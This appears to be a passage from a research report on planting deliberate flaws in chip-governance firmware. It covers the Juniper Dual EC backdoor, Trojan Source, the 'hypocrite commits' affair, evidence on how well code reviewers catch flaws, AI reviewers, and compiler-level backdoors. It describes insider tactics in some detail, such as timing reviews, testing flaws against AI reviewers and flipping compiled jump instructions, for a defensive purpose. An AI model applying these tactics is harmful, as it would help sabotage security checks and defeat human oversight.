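Whoever tampered with Juniper's ScreenOS in 2012 did not need to alter the program's logic. ScreenOS runs the company's NetScreen devices, which encrypt traffic between offices over a virtual private network (VPN). The encryption keys came from Dual EC, a random number generator designed by the US National Security Agency. Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues reconstructed the case by reverse-engineering dozens of ScreenOS versions in *Where Did I Leave My Keys?* (2018).

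Dual EC uses two fixed points on an elliptic curve, *P* and *Q*. Anyone can multiply a point by a number, but nobody knows a practical way to work backwards from the result to the number. The generator holds a secret number *s*₁. It outputs most of the x-coordinate of *s*₁*Q*, then takes the x-coordinate of *s*₁*P* as its next secret, *s*₂. Suppose, however, that someone chose *Q* so that they know a number *d* for which *P* = *dQ*. They can multiply the point behind the output by *d*:

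*d*(*s*₁*Q*) = *s*₁(*dQ*) = *s*₁*P*

The x-coordinate of the answer is *s*₂, and an attacker who knows *s*₂ can predict all the generator's later output. ScreenOS revealed 30 of the 32 bytes of the first x-coordinate, so an attacker had to try only 65,536 possibilities for the other two bytes.

In 2012 someone replaced Juniper's *Q* with another point and changed the expected answer in a self-test that would otherwise have failed. Juniper's official releases contained the new point for more than three years. Testing the output could not have exposed the change, because the numbers look equally random with either point to anyone who does not know *d*. To confirm that the attack worked, Checkoway and colleagues put their own *Q* into the firmware of a real device and decrypted its VPN connections.

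Juniper disclosed the problem in December 2015 after an internal code review, along with an administrator password that someone had added to the code by April 2013. Checkoway and colleagues describe those responsible as intruders, but they could examine only the firmware, and Juniper would not give further details. Juniper first tried to fix the problem by restoring its original *Q*. That helped only if nobody knew *d* for the original point either, and Juniper never explained how it had generated that point.

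### Text that displays differently from how it compiles

The text a reviewer sees on screen can differ from what the compiler processes. In 2021 Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge published a way to exploit this, which they called Trojan Source. Unicode, the standard for encoding text, includes invisible control characters for mixing left-to-right scripts such as English with right-to-left ones such as Arabic. An attacker can put these characters inside comments or quoted text to rearrange what a reviewer sees. A line that looks like active code may be part of a comment, which the compiler ignores, or the reverse. Boucher and Anderson demonstrated the method in C, Java, Python and several other languages. They also described a related trick in which two function names look identical but contain different characters, such as a Latin and a Cyrillic "H".

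Tools now catch much of this. GitHub shows a warning on files that contain the control characters, and the Rust compiler rejects them by default in comments and quoted text. GCC, a widely used C compiler, has warned about them since version 12, but by default only where a control character lacks its closing partner. A firmware team can also automatically reject any source file with characters outside the basic English set, since chip code rarely needs them. This is the easiest method in this section to block. It is also the hardest to pass off as an honest mistake, because a programmer would not type an invisible reordering character by accident.

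### Changes that are harmless on their own

The swapped constant in ScreenOS was useful only because of earlier changes. Researchers had publicly described the weakness in Dual EC in 2007. Juniper said in 2013 that its devices were safe because a second generator, called X9.31, processed Dual EC's output before anything else used it. Checkoway and colleagues found that the second generator never ran. They traced the failure to version 6.2, released in October 2008, in which Juniper had:

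- added Dual EC to supply the second generator's starting values;
- started fetching new starting values on every call instead of every 10,000 calls;
- made a loop counter and an output area global, so that two functions shared them;
- lengthened a random number that the device sends openly at the start of each VPN connection from 20 bytes to 32.

Fetching the starting values set the shared counter to 32, the point at which the second generator's loop stops. The loop therefore never ran, and the raw Dual EC output was still in the shared area when other code read its random numbers from there. The attack needs at least 26 bytes of that output, and the longer number sent at the start of each connection revealed enough. The attack required all four changes. A fifth change, which generated some random numbers in advance, often let an attacker decrypt a connection after observing only that connection.

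As far as Checkoway and colleagues know, Juniper's own engineers made the 2008 changes, and no public evidence shows they meant harm. The flaw was still very hard to see. Several experienced researchers who knew the function probably contained a bug missed the shared counter, and so did the laboratory that certified ScreenOS against a US government standard.

*S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2025) reports a September 2024 discussion of this type of attack with 12 practitioners from nine companies. It notes that a commit may look benign in isolation but become malicious in combination with others. The participants usually relied on human review, and none could point to a good solution. A reviewer who sees only the changed lines would find it hard to notice such a combination, especially if the changes were made months apart.

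An attacker may not need to write every part of a vulnerability. Wu and Lu, in *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, call a flaw that lacks one ingredient an "immature vulnerability". Their main example is use-after-free, in which a program frees a piece of memory and then uses it again, after an attacker may have changed its contents. The flaw requires a step that frees the memory, a step that uses it, and an order that puts the use after the free. If the code already has two of these, a small patch can add the third while appearing to fix something else.

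Honest developers also introduce vulnerabilities with code that looks correct. One patch to the Linux kernel added a single line to release memory after an error, which looked like good practice. But another function already released the same memory, and the resulting vulnerability lasted five years. Wu and Lu collected 138 known kernel vulnerabilities introduced by small, well-meant patches.

### The "hypocrite commits" experiment

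Wu and Lu, of the University of Minnesota, also tested the method on the kernel's maintainers without telling them. They called their patches "hypocrite commits" because each would fix a minor problem while introducing a worse one. One researcher found suitable places in the code and prepared the patches within a week.

In August 2020 the kernel's developers received five patches from two invented people, "James Bond" and "George Acosta". The researchers later said that one was a sincere fix, sent under a false name because they had already set up their computer for the experiment. The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board traced what happened to all five. Its audit, *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (Mason, Rostedt and colleagues, 2021), gives this account of the other four:

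- Maintainers quickly rejected a patch that copied an earlier, well-known bad one. The first reply came after about seven hours.
- A reviewer replied to another after about four and a half hours, saw that it was wrong and suggested corrections, taking the sender for a beginner. The sender never followed up.
- A maintainer found a third patch incorrect after six days and proposed alternatives. The sender admitted the error and apologised for the trouble.
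- A maintainer accepted the fourth, and it entered the kernel's repository. It was harmless, because the researchers had misunderstood that part of the kernel and failed to create the flaw they intended.

Mason and colleagues concluded that developers had caught or ignored every invalid patch and that the review process had worked. Wu and Lu had presented the experiment as proof that the attack was practical. They described a procedure in which they would reveal the flaw once a maintainer said a patch looked good, but according to the audit, the reviewers found the faults themselves. Three bad patches are too few to show how reliable review is, however, and one of them was already notorious. Wu and Lu also assumed an attacker who was neither a developer nor a maintainer. A reviewer may well give a trusted colleague's patch less attention than one from an unknown "James Bond".

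The experiment became public in November 2020, when a leading security conference accepted the paper. The paper's four reviewers had placed it in the top 5% of submissions, according to *An IEEE statement on the UMN paper* (Corbet, 2021). Linderud, Torres-Arias and two other signatories objected in a letter to the conference's chairs, *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*, that the researchers had experimented on people with no sign of ethics board approval. The signatories also feared that bad patches could spread automatically to older versions of the kernel without the later corrections, and that overworked maintainers would struggle to identify the affected patches.

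That December, Wu and Lu (2020) defended their study in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*. They wrote that they had studied a process rather than individuals, that no faulty patch had gone beyond email, and that the university's ethics board had since ruled that the work was not human research. They had kept each patch under five lines to save reviewers' time, and had supplied proper fixes for three real bugs. They apologised for wasting maintainers' time but said they had found no better way to do the study. In a later apology, quoted in The Hacker News' *Minnesota University Apologizes for Contributing Malicious Code to the Linux Project*, they explained that maintainers would have been on the lookout for the patches if asked for permission.

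That difficulty is real, but it does not justify their choice. One reader, commenting on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), argued that companies test their staff with fake phishing emails. Another replied that somebody senior authorises such tests and that employees have usually agreed to them in their terms of employment. Nobody in charge of the kernel had authorised this one. In IEEE's *2021 PC Statement* (2021), the conference's committee suggested a controlled experiment on a simulated project, which would have produced equal or better science with much less potential for harm. A chipmaker could test its own reviewers with planted flaws if management approved the exercise and someone ensured that no flaw reached a release.

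The dispute escalated in April 2021, when the university sent a new batch of poor patches. Many developers assumed the experiment had resumed, although the researchers said the patches came from an unrelated bug-finding project. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior maintainer, stopped accepting contributions from the university and proposed removing its earlier ones until somebody had reviewed them again. Five days later the researchers withdrew the paper. Wu and Lu (2021) told the conference in a letter that the design was inappropriate because they had studied the kernel community without proper consent, and that they should have worked with it from the start.

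The audit covered 435 commits. Reviewers found 349 correct and 39 in need of removal or repair, including the harmless patch from "George Acosta". Other developers had already corrected another 25. Of the rest, 12 no longer mattered, nine predated the research group, and the author of one faulty commit asked for its removal. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) accepted these results but added four patches sent from a visiting student's account, which the board had missed.

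### Why governance firmware is both exposed and checkable

The logic that decides whether a chip may run can be very small. In Petrie's licensing design, it consists mainly of a few comparisons, a counter and a stored public key. Petrie expects the mechanism to be simpler than Nvidia's 2021 limits on cryptocurrency mining, because the firmware does not need to tell one kind of work from another.

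Almost any mistake that makes a licence check more lenient is useful to a smuggler. The comparison might accept one value too many, the counter might fail to advance in some rare situation, or the code might treat an error during the signature test as a pass. Most mistakes in a large program such as the Linux kernel are useless to an attacker, and Wu and Lu needed special tools to find promising places in it. A competent engineer could make any of the licence-check mistakes by accident, and none requires a concealed program like the one in xz utils, so the insider only has to tell the buyer which mistake to exploit.

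The stored key is vulnerable in the same way as Juniper's constant. Checkoway and colleagues note that *Q* acted as a public key and *d* as its private key, so whoever replaced *Q* had in effect changed the lock on an existing door. They add that creating such a door from nothing usually requires far more invasive changes. Governance firmware contains such a door by design, because it is built to carry out commands from whoever holds the regulator's private key.

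But a small check is also much easier to examine completely. One participant in the discussion that Rahman and colleagues reported compared finding malicious commits to the halting problem, the problem of predicting whether a program will ever finish, which no method can solve for every program. That limit applies to programs in general, but a routine that compares a few fixed-size numbers and always finishes has a finite number of possible inputs, and a team can state exactly what it should do for each.

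A new licence number can only be lower than the old one, equal to it or higher, and a test of the equal case would expose a `>=` in place of a `>`. Ordinary tests are less useful for finding a hidden exemption for one device. If device numbers have 64 bits, there are about 1.8 × 10¹⁹ of them, and trying them all at a billion a second would take nearly 600 years. Formal verification avoids this search by proving mathematically what code does for every input, though it is far more practical for a short routine than for a whole operating system.

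Checking the key is even simpler, because anyone with the firmware's contents can compare the stored key with the one the regulator publishes and confirm that there is no second key. Outsiders had no such reference for Juniper's *Q*. But the reference copy has to come from outside the firmware team, because the person who changed *Q* also changed the self-test that should have detected the change.

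These checks cover only the code they examine, and a flaw elsewhere can defeat even a perfect licence check. If all the firmware shares the same memory, a use-after-free error in the fan-control code could let an attacker overwrite the usage meter. The firmware might also never call the licence check, just as ScreenOS never ran its second generator. Petrie warns that users may find ways to run a chip without triggering the usage checks, and suggests tying the checks to frequent operations that are hard to disable. Checkoway and colleagues recommend writing cryptographic code so that a reader can understand each function without looking elsewhere. For governance firmware, this would mean a short, separate module with its own protected memory, and an alert to reviewers whenever someone changes the module or the code that calls it.

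### Telling sabotage from accident

A planted flaw can be identical to an honest mistake, so an investigator can't establish intent from the code alone. Even the 2003 line could have been a typing error. It looked deliberate mainly because of the break-in and the false attribution, and because wait4 doesn't need to deal with user IDs. If Miller had submitted it himself through the normal process, he could have said he left out an equals sign, and many programmers would have believed him.

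The Minnesota case shows how badly people can misjudge intent in both directions. The reviewer who tried to teach a supposed beginner didn't realize that the submitter knew the patch was bad. The maintainer who received an apology had just caught a deliberate attempt at sabotage, but had no reason to treat it as one. Once the experiment was public, people began to suspect honest work too. Kroah-Hartman proposed the removals in *Revertion of all of the umn.edu commits*, where he took the fact that developers had already undone or repaired some of the patches as proof that the submissions were "almost universally wrong". The audit then found that 80% of the submissions were correct.

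About 15% of the university's commits contained errors, and the board removed or corrected the ones that remained, whatever their authors had intended. A chipmaker would be wise to fix flaws regardless of intent too, and to judge each one by what it would let someone do. It can also look for patterns, such as one developer whose mistakes keep weakening the same check. But if honest developers make errors at anything like that rate, one deliberate flaw a year would not stand out. Rahman and colleagues say it is still an open question which signals reliably distinguish bugs from deliberately malicious code.

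Prosecutors have succeeded where the developer left other evidence. Davis Lu was a software developer at a company in Beachwood, Ohio, from 2007 to 2019. The Hacker News' *Kill-Switch Malware* (2025), citing Cleveland.com, identifies the company as Eaton, which makes power-management equipment. According to the Justice Department's *Chinese National Who Deployed "Kill Switch" Code on Employer's Network*, Lu began sabotaging the company's systems after a 2018 reorganisation reduced his responsibilities and access. By August 2019 he had planted code that crashed servers by endlessly creating new tasks. He also deleted colleagues' profile files and wrote a kill switch that would lock out every user if the company disabled his account. The kill switch activated when the company put him on leave on 9 September, affecting thousands of users around the world. A jury convicted him in March 2025,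 and a judge sentenced him to four years in prison that August.

Lu's code was bound to attract attention, because it was designed to cause an outage and the outage began when his own account stopped working. He named the function "IsDLEnabledinAD", short for "Is Davis Lu enabled in Active Directory", the company's directory of users. He called another program "Hakai", the Japanese word for destruction, according to *Chinese National Sentenced to Prison for Deploying Destructive Computer Code* from the U.S. Attorney's Office. On the day he had to return his laptop, he deleted encrypted data, and his search history showed that he had looked up how to hide processes and delete files quickly.

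An insider who loosened a comparison in a licence check would cause no outage and would not need a function whose name revealed its purpose. If an investigator found the flaw, a prosecutor would still need evidence from outside the code, such as a payment or a message, to show that it was deliberate.

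## How often code reviewers catch security flaws

A reviewer can catch a flaw without working out whether it is deliberate. To measure how often reviewers notice flaws, researchers have given developers code with known flaws and examined years of past reviews at large software projects. The results depend heavily on the type of flaw and on whether the reviewers were asked to think about security.

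### Telling reviewers to look for security problems

Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021), in *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, asked 146 people, most of them software professionals, to review about 140 lines of Java code for managing employees' holidays. The researchers did not mention security at first. Each participant's code contained one of two flaws, both caused by failing to check user input. One version allowed SQL injection, a standard topic in security textbooks, in which an attacker types part of a database command into an ordinary field and the program runs it. The other version accepted any whole number, including a negative one that would benefit the user unfairly.

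On a first reading, 52 of 80 participants (65%) found the SQL injection, but only 14 of 66 (21%) found the missing check for negative numbers. The researchers then revealed that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what or where it was, and invited those who had missed it to look again. Thirteen more people found the SQL injection and seven more found the missing check. The remaining 60 participants, or 41% of the total, never found the flaw in the code they reviewed.

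The less famous flaw, a missing check for negative numbers, is more relevant to governance firmware because Petrie's licensing design has to reject a licence with a negative allowance. Four in five reviewers overlooked the flaw. The code also contained an ordinary bug, which about half the participants found. Eight of those who overlooked the missing check said they had mistaken this bug for the vulnerability. An insider could exploit that tendency by leaving a small, obvious mistake for the reviewer to find.

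A second experiment tested whether instructions help. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) randomly divided 150 participants into four groups and gave them the same 160 lines of code for registering website users. The code had two flaws. When a database error occurred, the program wrote the user's email address and unencrypted password to a log file. It also protected stored passwords with MD5, a hash function that researchers broke long ago. One group received no special instructions, and the other three were told to look for security problems. Two of those three also had to work through a checklist. One group's checklist had 22 general items, and the other's had seven items chosen to suit the code.

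| Instructions | Participants | Found the password in the log | Found the broken hash function |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| The same, with a general checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with a tailored checklist | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

Braz and colleagues report that participants who received security instructions were eight times more likely to find a flaw. That figure is a ratio of odds, where odds are the number of people who found a flaw divided by the number who didn't. Of the 117 people with instructions, 84 found at least one flaw and 33 found none, for odds of about 2.5. Without instructions, eight found a flaw and 25 didn't, for odds of 0.32. The share of people who found a flaw tripled, from 24% to 72%, which is still a very large effect for one sentence of instruction.

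The checklists made no significant difference, even though both included items that pointed to the two flaws. Many participants who missed the broken hash function said they did not know MD5 was unsafe, and a reminder to check the hash function does not help someone who thinks MD5 is safe. Two security engineers who tried the task beforehand found both flaws. Two people are too few to estimate a rate, but their result fits the participants' view that knowledge matters.

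Prompting helped reviewers in two experiments with four different flaws, although the same research group ran both. The finding on checklists rests on one experiment. Each participant reviewed only one change, so neither experiment tested whether an instruction still works after a reviewer has read it many times.

Few developers seem to think about security when reviewing code unless prompted. Braz and Bacchelli (2022), in *Software Security during Modern Code Review*, asked 182 practitioners what kinds of problem they look for when reviewing, and only nine mentioned security. Once asked about security, 111 said they always consider it. More than half of the respondents worked on security-sensitive software.

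### What reviewers miss in real projects

Experiments use invented code and volunteers who have never seen it before. *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* (Paul, Turzo and Bosu, 2021) instead examines how developers reviewed their own project, Chromium OS, Google's operating system for laptops, where every change needs a review. The study used a case-control design, which starts from known outcomes and looks backwards for differences. From 404,878 reviews, the researchers identified 516 in which a reviewer had caught a security flaw. They also traced flaws that were fixed later to the changes that introduced them, and found 374 reviews that had missed such a flaw.

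The researchers found the successes by searching reviewers' comments for words such as "overflow" and the failures by searching a bug tracker, so the 58% share of successes is a poor measure of how often reviewers catch flaws. Neither group includes flaws that nobody has discovered, and a competent insider's flaw would probably go undiscovered.

Reviewers caught some types of flaw far more often than others. They caught all 53 uses of functions known to be dangerous and 71 of 75 failures to release memory or other resources. A reviewer can recognise these from a few lines of code. Reviewers caught only 9 of 81 failures to validate input, 8 of 66 failures of access control, and 3 of 65 cases in which a program used a resource after releasing it. They caught none of the 13 failures to verify that data was authentic.

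A licence check validates a number, verifies a signature and decides whether to grant access. Almost all of its code is therefore of the types in which reviewers missed flaws. According to Paul and colleagues, reviewers tend to miss flaws that they could see only by running the code or understanding a large part of the program. Putting the licence check in a short, separate module would leave reviewers less code to understand, but they would still have to think about what the code fails to do.

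The researchers then built a statistical model from features of each review. Given one review that caught a flaw and one that missed a flaw, the model could tell which was which about 91% of the time. A miss was more likely when:

- the change touched files in many directories, which was the strongest predictor;
- the reviewer had done many reviews in the project overall;
- the file had already been through many changes;
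- the change was not a bug fix (the odds of catching a flaw were 4.5 times higher in bug fixes).

Reviewers did better when they had often reviewed the same file before, when they and the author regularly reviewed each other's work, and when the review took longer. Surprisingly, reviewers with more general reviewing experience did worse. Paul and colleagues suggest that people who review a great deal may be tired or rushed, but they could not confirm either explanation. In the 2021 experiment by Braz and colleagues, the people who reviewed most often did better, so the evidence on experience is mixed.

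Reviewers rarely comment on security. *A security perspective on code review* (di Biase, Bruntink and Bacchelli, 2016) found that about 1% of review comments in Chromium, the browser project, concerned it. *Security Defect Detection via Code Review* (Yu, Fu and colleagues, 2023) found an even lower share in four projects from OpenStack, which makes cloud-computing software, and Qt, a toolkit for graphical programs. The researchers searched 432,585 comments for security-related words, read the 20,995 that matched, and confirmed 614, or about one in 700. A keyword search misses some comments, and perhaps most changes had no security flaw to discuss. More than a third of the flaws that reviewers raised were race conditions, in which the result depends on the timing of two operations, and only 6% concerned improper access.

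Of the 539 confirmed flaws that reviewers raised, developers left 161 (30%) unresolved. When the discussion gave a reason, the most common was that the flaw was not worth fixing at that point, followed by disagreement between the author and the reviewer. Developers fixed 81% of flaws when the reviewer proposed a specific solution, but 60% when the reviewer only pointed out the problem. An insider whose flaw draws a comment but no proposed fix therefore has a fair chance of keeping it in the code by arguing that it is harmless, as honest developers often do.

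### How much a second reviewer helps

In an experiment published in 2013, researchers hired 30 web developers to review a small application with seven known vulnerabilities, and none of them found all seven. According to Braz and colleagues, the researchers concluded that manual review could be impractical because finding a flaw may take several reviewers. More experienced developers were not necessarily more accurate. Developers who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones, so a team that adds reviewers to catch more flaws should expect more false alarms too.

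Suppose one reviewer misses a flaw with probability *m*. If a second reviewer is equally good and works independently, both miss it with probability *m*². With *n* such reviewers, all of them miss it with probability *mⁿ*.

Of the 33 people given no instructions, 26 missed the broken hash function, so *m* is about 0.79. Two independent reviewers would both miss it 62% of the time, and it would take 13 to bring the chance that all of them miss it below 5%. Of the 41 people whose only help was an instruction to look for security problems, 16 missed it, so *m* is about 0.39. Two such reviewers would both miss it 15% of the time, and it would take four to get below 5%. By this calculation, one reviewer with the instruction is about as good as four without it. A company that wants better reviews should probably tell its reviewers to look for security problems before it doubles their number.

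But real reviewers are not independent, partly because they find the same things difficult. Imagine that half of all flaws are easy and each reviewer misses them 10% of the time, while the other half are subtle and each reviewer misses them 90% of the time. On average a reviewer misses half of all flaws, so *m*² predicts that two reviewers would both miss a quarter. In fact, both miss an easy flaw 1% of the time (0.1²) and a subtle one 81% of the time (0.9²), which averages 41%. More generally:

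*probability that both miss* = *m*² + *the variance of the miss rate*

The variance measures how much the miss rate varies across flaws and situations. It is zero only if every flaw is equally hard to find in every situation, so *m*² is the best case for two reviewers who find the same things difficult.

Shared assumptions increase the variance. Two engineers who learned the same outdated facts about MD5 will both approve its use. They may also both think security is someone else's job. One participant who missed the hash function told Braz and colleagues, "I would assume there would be some separate security assessment." Time pressure has a similar effect, because both reviewers are in a hurry the night before a release.

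A second reviewer helps less if they defer to the first. If they accept the first reviewer's approval half of the time, two reviewers without instructions would miss the hash function 70% of the time instead of 62%. Both may also defer to a senior author, in which case adding a reviewer achieves little. Paul and colleagues suspected that experienced authors receive less scrutiny, but in the Chromium OS data, the number of changes an author had previously submitted made no significant difference. That number is only a rough measure of seniority, and a chip company may have a stricter hierarchy than an open-source project.

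The number of reviewers made no significant difference in Chromium OS either. Reviewers may tend to miss the same flaws, but the project may also assign more people to riskier changes, which would hide any benefit. Di Biase and colleagues found some evidence in the browser project that reviews with more than two reviewers were better at finding security problems. The case for a second reviewer therefore relies more on calculation than on observed results, and the calculation is valid only if reviewers miss flaws independently of each other, which is true of few teams.

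### When the author wants the flaw to pass

Almost all of this evidence concerns accidental flaws. In the experiments, researchers planted a typical mistake in code by an anonymous author, and in the project studies nearly all the developers were presumably trying to write good code. An insider would choose a subtle flaw, which in the example above gets past two reviewers 81% of the time, compared with 41% for a random flaw.

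An insider can also choose the conditions of the review. To exploit the factors that predicted missed flaws in Chromium OS, they could spread the change over many directories, put the flaw in a file that changes constantly, and ask for a review from a busy colleague who doesn't know that file. They can wait until a deadline is close, or until the one engineer who understands the licence check is on holiday. Regularly reviewing each other's work helped colleagues catch accidental flaws, perhaps because they knew each other's weaknesses, but an insider could use the same familiarity to learn what a particular reviewer never checks.

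The "hypocrite commits" experiment comes closest to testing reviewers against a deceptive author, but its faulty patches came from strangers. No experiment described here has measured how well reviewers catch a flaw that a trusted colleague has designed for them to miss. The published detection rates are probably too high for that case. Engineers at a chipmaker might do better than the participants in the experiments, though, because they know their own code and can run it, while the participants had only a web page and gave it only a few minutes' attention.

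At the September 2024 meeting that Rahman and colleagues reported, practitioners described human review as error-prone. Some suggested requiring several reviewers, but most open-source packages have only one or two active maintainers. Others proposed tracking developers' reputations, but an attacker can steal a reputable developer's account, and honest newcomers have no reputation yet. The participants concluded that analysing code changes was not enough on its own.

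Eighteen practitioners from 17 organisations discussed the subject again in March 2025 (Lin, Ghebremichael and colleagues, 2025, *S3C2 Summit 2025-03*). Several said that they trust no change and assume that any of them could be malicious. One participant argued that a reviewer can learn little about a person's intentions from a single change, and would learn more from everything the person has submitted over time. This would have helped little with Jia Tan, whose first two years of work on xz utils looked harmless. Another participant said that "build scripts is where everyone has blind spots". These are the opinions of a small, self-selected group, although its members are responsible for such defences.

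### AI systems as reviewers

Many teams now have an AI system review each change before or instead of a person. An AI reviewer does not get tired, and teams can tell it to look for security problems every time. But its performance is hard to measure. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (2026) points out that an AI reviewer can correctly call a change dangerous for the wrong reason. If it objects to something harmless, the developer may fix that and leave the real flaw in place, much as eight participants in the 2021 experiment stopped at the wrong bug. The paper therefore proposes a test that gives the reviewer credit only for identifying the planted flaw and the code that proves it.

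Nobody has a complete list of the flaws in a real project to check an AI reviewer's findings against. Perhaps for this reason, *LLM-based Vulnerability Detection at Project Scale* (2026), whose tests include the coding agent Claude Code, counts false alarms in its trials on recent projects rather than the share of flaws found. A low false-alarm rate makes a tool pleasant to use, but it doesn't measure how often the tool misses a backdoor.

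AI already saves reviewers time on the narrower task of checking warnings from static analysis tools, which examine code without running it and produce many false warnings. In an industrial test described in *Reducing False Positives in Static Bug Detection with LLMs* (2026), the best AI method sorted real warnings from false ones with 93% to 94% accuracy. Its explanations cut the time a person needed to check a warning from about ten minutes to three. The method cannot find a flaw that the static analysis tool missed.

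Results for general AI reviewers are less encouraging. *From Industry Claims to Empirical Reality* (2026) analysed 3,109 pull requests (code changes submitted for review), most or all of them written by AI agents. Projects accepted 45% of those that only an AI had reviewed, compared with 68% of those that only people had reviewed. The study also examined 98 rejected requests that only an AI had reviewed. In 60% of them, at most 30% of the AI's comments were useful. The acceptance rate is a poor measure of security, though, because a strict reviewer would also lower it, and people may have chosen to review the more promising changes themselves.

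The agents in that study are also older than the best models of December 2026, and error rates in this field go out of date within months. *GitHub's Copilot Code Review* (September 2025) warned that AI reviewers were inconsistent, especially with new or disguised flaws. Today's models are much stronger, so a chipmaker should test them on its own firmware instead of relying on published figures.

Two difficulties are likely to remain even as models improve. The first is getting independent reviews. *Reducing False Positives in Static Bug Detection with LLMs* recommends running one model three times and taking the majority answer. This evens out random errors, but all three runs have the same gaps in understanding. A model that reviews code it wrote itself may also repeat its own mistake. Combining a person with an AI system, or two unrelated models, should come closer to *m*².

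An insider who has access to the company's AI reviewer, as most engineers would, can also privately test a flaw on it and revise the code until the reviewer no longer flags it. Nobody could do this with a human colleague without arousing suspicion. A company could make this kind of evasion harder by running a second model that its developers cannot use, and by keeping records of what they submit to the first.

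### The effect of AI-written code on human review

AI has also increased the amount of code that people have to review. In June 2025, a software company with several hundred engineers set a goal of doubling the number of accepted changes per engineer within a year. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) followed 802 of its developers and 196,212 pull requests from January 2024 to April 2026. The company reached its goal in the tenth month, by which time it labelled about 90% of its changes as AI-written and each reviewer was handling about twice as many changes as before. Within months of the announcement, automated reviews covered more changes than human reviews, and people increasingly approved changes without leaving a comment.

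The share of changes that developers later undid did not rise, nor did the number of fixes after acceptance. This is good evidence that ordinary quality held up, at least at one company with generous access to AI tools. It is much weaker evidence about sabotage, because a well-made backdoor causes no fault that would lead anyone to undo or fix it. If silent approvals mean that reviewers are reading less carefully, a planted flaw would be more likely to get through, and the company's statistics would not show it.

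*These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues, 2026) examined 33,596 AI-written pull requests in fairly popular open-source projects on GitHub. It found no recorded review for 61% of them. Of the rest, 59% had only AI reviewers, so a person helped review just 16% of the total.

Much of this gap seems to come from differences between projects rather than from the use of AI. When Duma and colleagues also compared AI-written and human-written changes within the same projects, they found that a person had helped review about 30% of the AI-written changes and 31% of the human-written ones. But about a quarter of human comments on AI-written changes were instructions to an AI agent, such as a request to fix an error, compared with under 2% on human-written changes. A person who tells an agent to fix a failed test may count as a reviewer in the project's records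 without having evaluated the code.

Other studies have mixed findings. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) cites an analysis of 278,790 review conversations in which people went through 11.8% more rounds of review for AI-generated code than for human-written code. That could mean greater care or just more mistakes to correct. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (2026) notes that researchers disagree about whether AI-written changes are larger, and that a quick approval might reflect confidence or a superficial look. *Plausible Is Not Enough* (2026) adds that review records reveal little about how individual reviewers judge AI-written code.

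The heavier review load helps an insider whatever its average effect on quality, because a busy reviewer is easier to find. An engineer caught with a weakened licence check can also blame the AI model that wrote it, and colleagues who see such errors every week will find this believable. Many open-source projects have responded by allowing AI assistance but requiring contributors to disclose it and a person to take responsibility for the result, according to *Plausible Is Not Enough*. A chipmaker could adopt the same rule and also keep each engineer's prompts, since a request to weaken the check would be evidence of intent.

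## Changing the build instead of the source

A build engineer, or anyone who gains a build engineer's access, can leave the source untouched and change what the build system makes from it. The backdoor then appears in no commit, so even a reviewer who caught every flaw in the source would miss it.

### What a source reviewer never sees

In Petrie's design, a reviewer can see that the source tests the licence number with a `>`. The compiler turns this into a comparison followed by a jump that depends on the result. On Intel-compatible processors, the codes for "jump if above" and "jump if above or equal" differ by a single bit. Someone who flips that bit in the compiled file before it is hashed changes the `>` to a `>=` without touching the source.

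A build engineer also has options that need less knowledge of machine code:

- **Build settings.** Firmware teams often include a switch that leaves out a check, so that engineers can test chips without a licence. If that setting is stored on the build server, nobody reviewing the source can tell which version will ship.
- **Libraries.** The reviewed code may call a library function to verify the regulator's signature. The build engineer can supply a version of the library that also accepts signatures from another key.
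- **Source files.** The build server can compile a different version of a file and then put the original back.
- **The compiler.** A modified compiler can add code to whatever it compiles.

The altered script in the xz utils release archive also ran during the build. A build engineer can make such changes directly on the build server.

### Thompson's compiler

Replacing the compiler is the hardest of these changes to detect. Ken Thompson, a co-creator of Unix, explained why in his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (1984). He wanted a secret password that would let him log in to a Unix system as any user. If he added it to the login program, anyone reading that program's source would find it. He could instead alter the compiler to add the password whenever it compiled the login program. That would keep the login source clean, but anyone reading the compiler's source would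 find the change.

Two facts let him clean up the compiler's source as well. The first is that a program can print its own source code. This line of Python, which Cox (2023), in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*, gives as an example, does so:

`s='s=%r;print(s%%s)';print(s%s)`

The text in quotation marks is a template for the whole line, and the program prints the template with a copy of the template inserted into it. A longer program can reproduce any amount of additional code in the same way.

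The other fact is that programmers write the C compiler in C, so they need an existing compiler binary to compile each new version. Information can therefore pass from binary to binary without appearing in the source. Thompson's example was `\v`, C's notation for the vertical tab character. When programmers first add it, the compiler's source has to state that `\v` means character number 11. Once they have compiled that version, they can replace the 11 in the source with `\v`. The number is then only in the binary, which passes it on to each new compiler it compiles.

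Thompson's attack combines the two:

1. Add two routines to the compiler's source. One recognises the login program and inserts the secret password. The other recognises the compiler's own source and inserts both routines, using the self-printing method.
2. Compile this source with a clean compiler, and install the result as the official compiler.
3. Delete both routines from the source.
4. Wait for someone to compile the clean compiler source. The installed binary adds both routines to the new compiler, which then adds the password to the login program.

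Reading the source code no longer reveals the backdoor, and recompiling everything from clean source does not remove it. Thompson added that the same attack would work in other programs that process code, and that it is harder to detect at lower levels of the system.

Thompson had actually built the backdoor. Cox asked him for the code in 2023 and ran it on a simulated 1970s Unix system. The code consists of 99 lines of C and a 20-line script, and inserts text into the source as the compiler reads it. The compromised compiler was about 20% larger than the clean one, at 12,918 bytes instead of 10,724. Thompson had once arranged for another group to copy it. A bug made their copy grow as it repeatedly compiled itself, so they noticed something was wrong and eventually got rid of the backdoor. According to course notes from NYU, researchers in 2009 found a worm called Induc that attacked the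 compiler for the Delphi language to insert code into the programs it compiled.

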